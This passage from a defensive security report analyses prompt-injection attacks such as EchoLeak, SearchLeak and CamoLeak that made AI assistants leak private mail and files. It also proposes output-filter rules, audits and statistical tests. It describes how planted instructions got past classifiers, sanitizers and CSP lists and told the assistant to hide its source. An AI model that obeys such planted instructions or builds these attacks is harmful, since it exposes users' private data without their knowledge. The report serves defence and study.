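The first defence was a classifier that checked incoming text for prompt injections. The researchers got past it by addressing the email to its human recipient and never mentioning an AI. Microsoft had assumed that an attack would look different from ordinary mail, but a request to a colleague and an instruction to an assistant can be the same sentence. Ravia blames a shortage of realistic attacks to train such classifiers on. Better training would lower the miss rate, but an attacker can try many wordings. If a classifier misses a share p of them, the chance that at least one of k independent attempts gets through is

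1 − (1 − p)ᵏ.

With a miss rate of 1% and 100 attempts, this is about 63%.

*EchoLeak* (Reddy and Gujral, 2025) proposes a firmer rule, under which Copilot would answer from internal sources by default and use outside email only when the user asks for it. The attacker's email would then rarely have reached the model. The rule doesn't suit an assistant that reports what came in overnight, but such an assistant could still keep internal documents out of the context while it summarizes a stranger's message.

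The second defence removed outside links and images from the answer. In Markdown, the address of a link or image can directly follow its text or stand on a separate line, like a footnote. Microsoft's filter recognised only the first form, but the program that displayed the answer recognised both. Willison (2025) thinks Microsoft forgot the second, less familiar form.

Adding that form to the filter would have closed this gap, but Markdown has many dialects and there could be others. A filter that ran after the Markdown had become HTML would have held, because both forms produce the same kind of tag:

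`<img src="https://images.example/dot.png">`

The third defence was the CSP, which limited the servers from which Copilot's page could load images. Ravia prints the list of allowed servers, which has 29 different entries, including 11 that cover every server under a given name. The researchers searched these servers for a service that would contact other addresses on request. They found one in SharePoint, but it worked only if the victim accepted an invitation to the attacker's site. They then found one in Teams that required no action from the victim.

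The CSP worked as designed, since the browser contacted only a permitted server. Microsoft had assumed that a permitted server wouldn't pass requests on to anyone else. Willison calls the Teams service an open redirect, a page that sends the browser on to another address. A redirect would have been less dangerous, because the browser checks redirects against the CSP too. In Ravia's account, the Teams server fetched the outside address itself, and a CSP doesn't control what servers do.

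Copilot also names the sources of its answers, which might have alerted the employee. But in their email, the researchers asked Copilot never to mention the message, supposedly for compliance reasons, and Copilot did not cite it. This safeguard relied on the model to report what had influenced it. The application can instead list the documents it retrieved without involving the model.

Ravia proposes the name "LLM scope violation" for an attack in which untrusted text directs a model to private data elsewhere in its context, and argues that a specific name will help developers build specific defences. Willison does not think the pattern is new, because models have never been able to take the source of a text into account. Willison is right about the cause, but Ravia's description suggests a check that ordinary software could make. If the context contained both a stranger's email and private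 files, the application could refuse to load anything that the answer refers to.

According to Reddy and Gujral, Microsoft started repairs in the spring and deployed the full fix on its servers in May 2025. Aim Labs published the attack on 11 June.

Reddy and Gujral also include a table matching eight defences to the steps of the attack. Their paper mentions "our tests", but they ran no experiments, so the table rests on reasoning alone. Parts of it are doubtful. They mark the internal-sources rule as unable to stop the theft, although they argue in the text that EchoLeak "fails by design" under such a rule. They also expect an image proxy with signed addresses to succeed, but an attack on GitHub, described below, got data out through one. Their case for a strict CSP is stronger, provided that the policy also blocks any of the company's own services that fetch other addresses.

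### SearchLeak

Varonis' *SearchLeak* (June 2026) described a one-click attack on the page where employees use Copilot to search company emails, meetings and files. The attacker sent the victim a link to Microsoft's real search page, with instructions in the part of the address that normally holds the search words. When the page opened, Copilot followed the instructions, found an email and put its subject line into an image address. Subject lines sometimes contain login codes, and Varonis warns that the method could also have reached meeting notes and company files.

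Microsoft had assumed that any words in the search field came from the user. Defences against hostile documents didn't help, because the instructions arrived as the user's own request. Phishing filters were also unlikely to flag the link, since it pointed to a genuine Microsoft site. If the page had filled in the search field but waited for the user to press Enter, the user could at least have read the words first.

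Microsoft did have a filter for dangerous HTML in Copilot's answers. It wrapped the answer in a code block, which makes a browser show tags as text. The timing was wrong:

1. The model began its answer, and the page displayed each piece as it arrived.
2. An image tag appeared, and the browser requested the image.
3. The model finished its answer.
4. The filter turned the image tag into harmless text.

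Programmers call this a race condition, because the result depends on which of two events happens first. Anyone who tested the filter by looking at finished answers would have concluded that it worked. The filter would have worked if Microsoft had applied it to each part of the answer before the browser displayed that part.

The image request still had to satisfy the CSP, which permitted Bing. Bing's search for similar pictures accepts the address of a picture and fetches the picture from Bing's own servers, so Bing delivered the email title to the attacker. As with Teams, the browser's CSP had no effect on a request that came from a server.

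Bing was already on the list that Ravia printed in 2025, so closing the route through Teams left a similar one open. One of the ReLeak attacks also got data out through Bing, and Microsoft patched it months after fixing SearchLeak. Microsoft seems to have closed one route at a time without removing Bing from the list. Cato AI Labs, the team behind ReLeak, had found EchoLeak under its former name, Aim Labs.

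Varonis points out that SearchLeak needed all three flaws, so fixing any one of them would have stopped it. Such flaws may go unfixed because each one looks harmless as long as the other defences work.

### Filters that looked for the wrong thing

Even a filter that runs at the right time and on the right text can miss some ways of loading a file. Embrace The Red's *Copirate 365 at DEF CON* describes a Copilot feature that previewed web pages inside the chat. Microsoft's filter removed image tags from the preview but left in style rules, which can also make a browser load files. Like MySpace's filter in 2005, it worked from a list of what to block. In Rehberger's demonstration, a user opened a shared Word document with planted instructions and typed only "hi there". Copilot then found an email and sent its contents to Rehberger's server.

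Another safeguard was that the preview normally stayed closed until the user opened it. This default offered no protection because the planted instructions could get Copilot to open the preview.

The CSP also varied from site to site, because it is set by the page that contains the chat, and Copilot appears on many Microsoft sites. Some policies allowed test servers and, apparently, domains that individual employees had added. A company that offers its assistant as a component for other websites has the same problem, since it can't know what policy each site will use. Rehberger reported the flaw on 16 October 2025, and Microsoft fixed it on 5 March 2026.

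Rehberger also got Copilot to save a malicious instruction in its long-term memory. Copilot then leaked passwords that the user mentioned in later conversations, even though the original document was no longer involved. Microsoft reported this fixed on 6 December 2025.

GitHub's design was more careful, but Legit Security's *CamoLeak* defeated it in June 2025. Copilot Chat on GitHub's website could load images only from GitHub's own servers. Outside images went through a proxy named Camo, which accepted an address only if it had a valid signature. GitHub computes this signature from the address and a secret key. A model can't compute the signature, so it can't put private data into a new address that Camo will accept.

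The researcher had GitHub sign a set of image addresses in advance, one for each letter and symbol, and put them in a hidden comment on a pull request. When another user asked Copilot Chat about the pull request, it displayed the images in an order that spelled out text from that user's private projects. Every address was valid, and the order of the requests revealed the text. In one test, the stolen text described a security flaw that its owners had not yet made public.

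GitHub had assumed that data could leave only inside an address. This method uses 40 images to leak a 40-character access key, so a limit of one image per answer would have spread the theft over 40 answers. GitHub turned off images in Copilot Chat that August, which was the more reliable fix.

### Data that leaves through a tool

Even a perfect filter on the displayed answer can't stop an agent from leaking data through its tools. Varonis' *CoSnitch* (2026) describes an attack on the consumer version of Copilot, which users can connect to accounts such as Gmail and Google Drive. As in SearchLeak, the victim clicked a link that contained instructions. Copilot then collected private data, added it to a web address and opened that address with its tool for summarizing pages. Neither a sanitizer nor a CSP could have blocked the request, because it didn't come from the browser. The request went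 out even if the victim closed the page immediately.

The link depended on an undocumented setting that made Copilot run a prompt as soon as the page loaded. The researchers learned of the setting from Copilot's own explanation of why prompts could not run automatically. Varonis reported the attack in December 2025. Microsoft patched the flaw, CVE-2026-24301, on 18 August 2026, according to TechRadar's *Experts manage to hack Microsoft Copilot by continually asking it questions*.

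PromptArmor demonstrated an attack on Atlassian's Rovo that used a similar tool. The victim uploaded a file with hidden instructions and asked Rovo to organize some Jira tickets. Rovo added data from the tickets to a web address and was able to open that address because nothing checked whether Rovo had put it together itself. An administrator could turn off web search for the whole organization, but this did not remove the tool for opening search results. If the victim returned to the chat later, they saw the suggested ticket changes but no trace of the theft.

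The Hacker News (2026) could not confirm a fix as of 8 August. It advises organizations to restrict which apps and groups can use Rovo. On a site with several Jira apps, blocking Rovo in one leaves the chat available through the others.

Atlassian fixed a separate flaw on 8 July, in which a link started a prompt in Rovo. Varonis' *RovoBlast* (2026) focuses on data leaving through Rovo's web research agent. According to The Hacker News, the attack reported on the bug-bounty site Bugcrowd used an image address instead and obtained an access key from Confluence. Blocking only one of these routes would have left the other open.

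### Whether criminals have used these attacks

None of the published accounts describes a theft by anyone other than researchers. Microsoft said that EchoLeak had not been exploited, according to SC Media's *Microsoft 365 Copilot ‘zero-click’ vulnerability enabled data exfiltration*. Microsoft's notice about SearchLeak, *M365 Copilot Information Disclosure Vulnerability* (2026), also lists the flaw as not exploited and says customers need to do nothing. Varonis saw no sign that anyone had used CoSnitch, and neither Rovo disclosure reports any real attacks.

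How much these statements prove depends on who could have noticed an attack. In EchoLeak and SearchLeak, the victim's browser contacted only Microsoft's servers, so an employer's network records would have shown normal traffic. Microsoft's servers made the final request to the attacker, so Microsoft could have searched its own logs for such requests. Its statements are therefore stronger evidence than a researcher's, but none of the accounts explains how it checked. Other traces may not exist. Rehberger found that, as of April 2026, Microsoft's documentation said changes to Copilot's memory left no entries in the audit log.

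Reddy and Gujral call EchoLeak the first "real-world" exploit of its kind. It was real-world in the sense that it worked on a product in everyday use, but the only people known to have used it are those who reported it.

A flaw can also get a high severity score without anyone ever using it, because the standard formula measures what an attacker could do. Microsoft rated SearchLeak as critical but scored it 6.5 out of 10, while the US National Vulnerability Database gave it 7.5, according to The Hacker News' *One-Click Microsoft 365 Copilot Flaw Could Have Let Attackers Steal Emails*. Microsoft's score accounts for the victim having to click. The formula gives 7.5 if no click is needed and everything else stays the same, which may fully explain the difference.

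### Rules for an output filter

These cases support four rules. Most concern the order in which an application does things, so they don't depend on recognising hostile text.

A filter should parse the answer with the same program that displays it. For a chat window, this means checking the finished HTML rather than the Markdown, as EchoLeak showed. The filter should also keep only the elements on an allow-list, because developers easily overlook an element that can load files, as the Copilot preview showed.

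Second, the application should sanitize the answer before the browser draws any of it. The simplest way is to wait for the whole answer, but users like to read while the model is writing. The application can instead convert and sanitize all the text so far whenever a new piece arrives, and display only the result. Sanitizing each piece separately isn't safe, because a tag may start in one piece and end in the next. The application also has to do this in a separate document where the browser loads nothing. In an ordinary page, the browser can request an image as soon as a script creates it, before the script adds it to the visible page.

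A chat window can avoid much of this difficulty by showing plain text while the model writes and adding links and formatting only after the finished answer has been checked.

Third, the CSP should not permit any address that can fetch content from other addresses. Varonis recommends reviewing the CSP for such services. This is hard with a list like Microsoft's, because an entry that covers every server under a domain also covers services that other teams add later. It is easier to permit a single server that hosts only the product's own icons and charts. The CSP should block fonts, stylesheets and everything else by default. If other websites embed the chat, its maker can put it in a frame with a separate CSP.

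Some products need to show outside pictures, such as those in search results. The application can copy these to its own server before the model reads any private data. The requests to outside servers then can't depend on that data, and an attacker can't see which of the copies the answer displays. This would have stopped CamoLeak, because Camo fetched pictures only when the browser requested them.

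Fourth, the same restrictions should apply to tools. A tool that opens web pages should refuse any address the model has put together itself. OpenAI's rule for ChatGPT, described earlier, works this way, and Google has published a similar one. Rehberger doubted in 2026 that Microsoft's Copilots had one yet. As with images, the application should also limit the number of requests.

The table applies the rules to the attacks, assuming that the rest of each product stayed as it was.

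| Attack | Parse as displayed, with an allow-list | Sanitize before display | No address that fetches others | Same restrictions for tools |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| EchoLeak | Stops it | No effect | Stops it | No effect |
| SearchLeak | Too late | Stops it | Stops it | No effect |
| Copilot's HTML preview | Stops it | No effect | Stops it | No effect |
| CamoLeak | No effect | No effect | Stops it | No effect |
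| CoSnitch | No effect | No effect | No effect | Stops it |
| Rovo, uploaded file | No effect | No effect | No effect | Stops it |

The third rule stops every attack in the table that used the display, so a developer who can make only one change to a chat window should add the list of permitted servers. In Rovo, the fourth rule would have blocked the route that PromptArmor demonstrated but not Markdown images, which Rovo also displayed.

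## Deciding how much formatting to allow, and testing it

### What users lose without formatting

A developer could satisfy most of the rules for output filters by showing every answer as plain text, but answers would then be harder to read and check. The loss to users and the gain in security vary between formatting elements.

Headings, lists, bold type and tables contain no web addresses, so a browser can display them without contacting a server. Removing them adds almost no security, as long as the sanitizer treats an image inside a table cell like any other image. When an employee asks which of six suppliers have replied, and at what price, a table makes the answer much easier to read.

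Images from external sources matter less in many products. A mail assistant can summarize a mailbox without them, and the application can draw its own charts. An assistant for shoppers or designers would lose much more without external images.

Links are harder to give up because readers use them to check answers. They also help against injections, since an employee is more likely to catch a false summary if the source is one click away. But even a helpful link can carry private data. OpenAI's *ChatGPT generated links* gives the example of a user who asks where to find cars nearby. ChatGPT might offer a link with "London" in its URL because it knows the user lives there. The link saves the user a search but also reveals their city to the car site. A filter can't reliably distinguish such a link from a malicious one.

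The model can cite its sources without writing addresses. The application has a record of which documents it retrieved, so the model can cite them by number and the application can add the links. In the mail assistant, each link can open the original email in the employee's mail program.

Interactive elements are most useful to people who are building something. In June 2025, Copilot Chat began previewing HTML files with outside resources such as images and JavaScript libraries, according to GitHub's *Improved attachments and larger context in Copilot Chat in public preview* (2025). Many pages don't work without their libraries, so a programmer couldn't judge them from a preview that blocked those libraries. But if the model writes the HTML, it can put private data into any address the preview loads. A safer preview would load copies of common libraries from the product's own server and block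 all other outside resources.

### What vendors restrict

The table compares five policies that vendors published or introduced in 2025 and 2026.

| Policy | What it blocks or limits | Cost to users | Published effect |
|---|---|---|---|
| Microsoft's defences | Known image leaks, certain untrusted links, some actions without approval | An extra step before some actions | No figures |
| Google Workspace | Unsafe addresses, risky combinations of tools, some actions without confirmation | Extra confirmations | Fewer successful attacks, no figures |
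| OpenAI's link check | Automatic loading of addresses its crawler hasn't seen | Warnings on new or uncatalogued pages | No figures |
| OpenAI's Lockdown Mode | Live browsing, web images, deep research, agent mode, file downloads | Loss of those features, outdated search results | No figures |
| GitHub Copilot Chat | Images in answers | No pictures or outside diagrams | No figures |

Microsoft (2025) distinguishes probabilistic defences, which make an attack less likely to succeed, from deterministic ones, which guarantee that a particular attack fails. It counts its block on image leaks as deterministic and says it also looked for variants of the flaw Rehberger had reported. SearchLeak and ReLeak still got data out through images in 2026. A deterministic block's guarantee applies only to the routes it covers. Where Microsoft can't block or detect an attack well enough, it asks for the user's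 consent. For example, Copilot can draft an email in Outlook, but the user has to send it.

Google's policy is easier to change quickly. *Google Workspace's continuous approach to mitigating indirect prompt injections* (Gavish, 2026) describes a central policy engine that controls confirmations, web addresses and the order in which an agent may use its tools. Staff can respond to a new attack by changing a setting, without retraining a model. Some of these quick fixes match known patterns of text, so they have the same weakness as MySpace's filter and work best as stopgaps. Google also has a good way to measure each defence, which is to simulate attacks on apps such as Gmail and Docs with and without it, but it hasn't published the results. The article's only percentage, 75%, refers to faster production of synthetic training data.

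OpenAI's link check, described earlier, checks each exact address instead of the website. OpenAI's *Keeping your data safe when an AI agent clicks a link* (2026) gives two reasons for not relying on a list of trusted sites. A trusted site may redirect the browser elsewhere, and a strict list causes so many warnings that people learn to click through them. The link check has a similar problem on a smaller scale, because ChatGPT asks for confirmation of every link to a site whose owner has asked OpenAI not to catalogue it. The check also covers only data leaking through the address, so the page may still be false or contain an injection.

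OpenAI has extended the idea to searches and page visits by its agents. If an agent is about to send out something it learned in the conversation, OpenAI either shows the user the data and asks for approval, or blocks the request and tells the agent to try another way. OpenAI's *Designing AI agents to resist prompt injection* (2026) argues that such limits are necessary because input classifiers usually miss well-developed attacks. It describes an attack email, reported by outside researchers in 2025, that looked like an ordinary message about staff restructuring and worked 50% of the time in testing with one particular user request.

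Lockdown Mode is much stricter. OpenAI recommends it for a small group, such as executives and security teams, and says most users don't need it (*Introducing Lockdown Mode and Elevated Risk labels in ChatGPT*, 2026). OpenAI released it to business customers in February 2026 and to personal accounts in June. Users can still upload and generate images, but ChatGPT reads only stored copies of web pages, which may be out of date.

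Even this setting leaves some routes open. According to OpenAI's *Lockdown Mode*, the setting doesn't affect the coding tool Codex and doesn't automatically disable every connected app in workspaces run by an administrator. OpenAI advises administrators to consider who can see the result of each action an app can take, since a public comment can also leak data.

After CamoLeak, GitHub chose a narrower restriction and turned off images in Copilot Chat's answers. It also blocked the attack's use of its image proxy, according to Petri's *GitHub Copilot Chat Hit by ‘CamoLeak’ Flaw Allowing Silent Data Exfiltration*. Users can still give Copilot images to analyze, a feature GitHub (2025) added that April. Legit Security's account of the fix doesn't mention the HTML preview, which shows why developers need to check each display separately.

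A university study provides better evidence of how often confirmations interrupt work. *LivePI* (Zhao, Bhaskar and Dobriban, 2026) tested a defence that filters incoming text, checks each tool call before it runs, and sends suspicious calls to a person for approval. With GPT-5.3-Codex, the defence stopped every attack in the test that would otherwise have succeeded. During ordinary work, it interrupted about nine of 899 tool calls (1.00%). The researchers designed the defence for their own test, so it might do worse elsewhere, but the result suggests that approval requests can be rare enough for people to read them.

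### The decision for the mail assistant

How much formatting to allow depends on which of Willison's three conditions the assistant already meets. The table shows how much the company's assistant could safely allow in three settings.

| Formatting | Public data only | Private data, trusted content | Private data, untrusted mail |
|---|---|---|---|
| Headings, lists, tables | Yes | Yes | Yes |
| The product's own icons and charts | Yes | Yes | Yes |
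| Outside images | Yes, through a proxy | No | No |
| Outside links | Yes | Only if copied exactly from a retrieved document | Only if copied exactly from the message in question |
| Links to internal sources | Not needed | Yes, added by the application | Yes, added by the application |
| Automatic link previews | Yes | No | No |
| Interactive elements | In a separate frame | Only the application's own buttons | Only the application's own buttons |

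An assistant limited to public data answers questions from public web pages and has no access to the mailbox. An injected image can then leak little, and a proxy hides the employee's IP address. But this protection also requires that the employee's questions, the chat history and any stored memories contain no private data. An employee who asks about a company that their employer secretly plans to buy has put private data into the conversation.

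An assistant that searches documents only staff can edit has private data and trusted content. Outside images are still a risk here, because a colleague can easily paste in a supplier's text or save a customer's PDF, and the documents then include an outsider's words. The company loses almost nothing by blocking these images, since they add little to answers about internal documents.

An agent that reads untrusted mail meets all three conditions as soon as its answers can load an outside address. The rule for exact links still allows the small leak described earlier, because the model's choice of link can carry information. If the email contains 64 links, a click on the one the model chose reveals up to log₂ 64 = 6 bits, or about one letter. The company can avoid this leak by linking only to the original email.

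A rough calculation shows why outside images aren't worth the risk in this setting. Suppose they save the employee 10 seconds per answer, and a leak costs the company 1,000 hours of work, or 3.6 million seconds. The images are then worth having only if fewer than

10 ÷ 3,600,000 = 1 in 360,000

answers leak data. Both figures are invented, and a company could substitute its own. But with any serious estimate of the damage, the acceptable rate is so low that tests of the model could hardly confirm it.

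### Auditing what arrives and what leaves

An audit should test what reaches the model separately from what the display loads. The steps are:

1. List every place where the product displays content, including the phone app, notifications, exported files, emailed summaries and any internal dashboard where staff read conversations. Include the team chats where people paste answers, since PromptArmor found that link previews there can leak data without a click.
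2. Put a different harmless code word in each place where text can hide: comments, metadata, image descriptions, white text, off-screen text, PDF layers, invisible characters and both versions of an email. Add one in plain view.
3. Save the exact input that the model receives and search it for the code words.
4. Send prepared test answers to each display without using the model. Cover every element that can load a file, with all addresses leading to a test server that the developer owns.
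5. Record outside requests from before the first word of the answer appears until well after the last one. Then reopen the conversation and check again.
6. Repeat the audit after every change to the model, the converter, the display or the content security policy.

The visible code word in step 2 is a control: if it doesn't reach the model, the test isn't working. The other code words show which hidden text gets through. If the one in the plain-text version of the email arrives but the one in the HTML version doesn't, the connector is reading a version that the employee's mail program normally doesn't display. A sender can then show the employee one message and give the model another. For images, the developer has to save the picture that the model receives and ask the model to list all the words it can read.

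Some hidden text may be useful, such as image descriptions that an assistant may need, so the developer has to decide which code words should reach the model. Because the code words contain no instructions, this part of the audit doesn't show whether the model would obey hidden instructions.

Step 4 leaves out the model because the model might refuse to write the test image, and the audit would then appear to succeed even if the display would have loaded the image. The test answers should arrive in small pieces, as real answers do, because SearchLeak worked only while the answer was still appearing.

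The developer needs to check both the browser's network log and the test server's log. If one of the product's own servers passes the data on, as in EchoLeak and SearchLeak, only the test server's log will show the leak.

The developer should also run the display test once on a test copy with the protections turned off. If no request reaches the server, the test can't detect a leak, so a clean result with the protections on doesn't show that they work.

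Products and attacks both change quickly enough to justify step 6. GitHub added image uploads and HTML previews to Copilot Chat within three months. OpenAI's *Continuously hardening ChatGPT Atlas against prompt injection attacks* (2025) describes an automated attacker, trained by reinforcement learning, that the company uses to search for new weaknesses in its Atlas browser. The display test needs no model, so developers can run it automatically before every release.

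### What 300 clean trials show

Testing whether the model obeys injections requires statistics, because the same model may resist an instruction once and follow it the next time. Suppose the developer sends the mail assistant 300 hostile emails and none succeeds. If the true failure rate is p and the trials are independent, the chance of this result is

(1 − p)³⁰⁰.

The highest rate compatible with the result at 95% confidence is the one that makes this chance 5%:

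p = 1 − 0.05^(1/300) ≈ 0.0099.

The true rate could therefore be as high as about 1%. At that rate, if 1,000 similar emails arrived in a year, about ten would succeed. The upper limit is roughly 3 ÷ n, where n is the number of clean trials. Showing a rate below 0.1% takes about 3,000 clean trials, and showing the rate of 1 in 360,000 from the image example would take more than a million.

The trials also have to be independent. If the 300 emails are 10 templates with 30 small variations each, and the template determines the result, the developer has run only 10 trials. The limit is then 1 − 0.05^(1/10), or about 26%. Similarly, a developer learns more from sending 300 different answers through a display filter than from sending the same prepared answer 300 times, which mostly repeats one test.

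Even 300 independent trials provide little evidence about how an agent will handle an attacker who adapts. The calculation gives a limit on the average failure rate for emails like those in the test, but an attacker keeps rewriting an email until it works.

In *BrowseSafe++*, Chen, Zhang and colleagues (2026) gave seven agents 1,024 tasks on pages with injections, most of them found on real websites. When an injection failed, another model used the agent's response to rewrite the injection, for up to 64 attempts per task.

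| Model running the agent | Tasks where the original injection succeeded | Tasks where any attempt succeeded |
|---|---|---|
| Claude Sonnet 5 | 2.05% | 30.66% |
| GPT-5.5 | 0.49% | 65.23% |
| Claude Haiku 4.5 | 0.59% | 78.81% |
| Gemini 3.1 Pro | 2.93% | 92.87% |
| Gemini 3.5 Flash-Lite | 4.00% | 93.55% |
| DeepSeek V3.1 | 2.93% | 95.02% |
| Kimi K2 | 0.59% | 95.41% |

With a failure rate of 0.49%, GPT-5.5 would have about a 23% chance of completing 300 independent trials without a failure. Yet the adaptive attacker succeeded on about two-thirds of the tasks. Some of the increase comes from allowing 64 attempts instead of one, but real attackers can also try more than once.

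Claude Sonnet 5 failed about four times as often as GPT-5.5 on the original injections, but less than half as often against the adaptive attacker. A developer who chose a model by its score on fixed attacks could choose the one that is weaker against an adaptive attacker.

The adaptive attacker also succeeded more often when it only had to change the agent's answer than when it had to make the agent change something else, such as a file or a message. Against GPT-5.5, it succeeded on 81.43% of the first kind of task and 28.52% of the second. Against Claude Sonnet 5, the figures were 40.57% and 7.90%. An image leak needs only a changed answer, so restricting what answers can load protects these agents in the category where attacks succeeded more often.

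### What benchmarks for browsing agents cover

Developers can compare models with public benchmarks, but *AutoPI* (2026) notes that most reported success rates still come from fixed sets of injections. Benchmarks also differ in what they measure. InjecAgent tests single, simulated tool calls, while WASP has agents carry out realistic tasks on websites. According to *Who Is Your Agent Serving?* (2026), WASP also distinguishes attacks that make some progress from those that reach their goal.

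BrowseSafe++ covers 12 types of website and 38,675 injected pages. Each injected page has a clean copy and is provided as HTML, Markdown, an accessibility tree and a screenshot. In 32,187 of the injected pages, the injection came from a page that a working browser agent had visited between September 2025 and September 2026. Most of the researchers work for Perplexity, which makes the Comet browser.

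The clean copies make it possible to measure false alarms. GPT-6 Astra, the general-purpose model with the best overall detection score, wrongly flagged between 13.82% and 15.10% of the clean pages, depending on the form. Models also followed injections they could recognize. Across 15 models, 74.15% of the injections that a model followed during a task were ones it had flagged in a separate detection test.

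BrowseSafe++ has important gaps in how it covers the problems that formatting causes. Chen and colleagues kept a page only if the injection appeared in all four forms. This makes the forms easier to compare but excludes text that reaches the model in one form and not in another. Most of what Khodayari and colleagues found on the web was text of this kind. About 250 pages are labelled "HTML comment", but a real comment wouldn't appear in a screenshot, so the label may describe where the injection originally was.

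The selection also favours injections that software can recognize. A classifier or a list of typical phrases first picked out the pages, and three language models then voted on them. An injection that all of these missed would be absent from the benchmark.

The third gap is that, in the adaptive test, the researchers checked the agent's final answer and the state of its test environment, but not what a browser would load when showing that answer. A good score is therefore not evidence about image leaks, and a developer still has to run the display test described above.

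Nguyen, Guo and colleagues (2026), in *INFUSE*, criticize WASP and a similar benchmark, WAInjectBench, for testing only injections in web pages. Their own benchmark tests agents that work through a command line, where instructions can also arrive in file names, settings or program output. Across 19 models, attacks succeeded in 19.6% of runs on average.

LivePI comes closest to the mail assistant because it uses real test accounts for email and chat. In a simulation, researchers can see that an agent tried to send an email, but not whether the message would have arrived. Depending on the model, between 10.7% and 29.6% of LivePI's 169 attacks succeeded. Every injection in a group chat worked, though there were only 15 per model. The researchers tested only one agent, OpenClaw.

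A public competition also tested whether attackers could hide a successful attack from the user, which matters for any policy that relies on users noticing something wrong. *How Vulnerable Are AI Agents to Indirect Prompt Injections?* (2026) reports more than 8,000 successful attacks on 13 models in 41 scenarios. AgentDojo and InjecAgent don't test whether attacks can be hidden.
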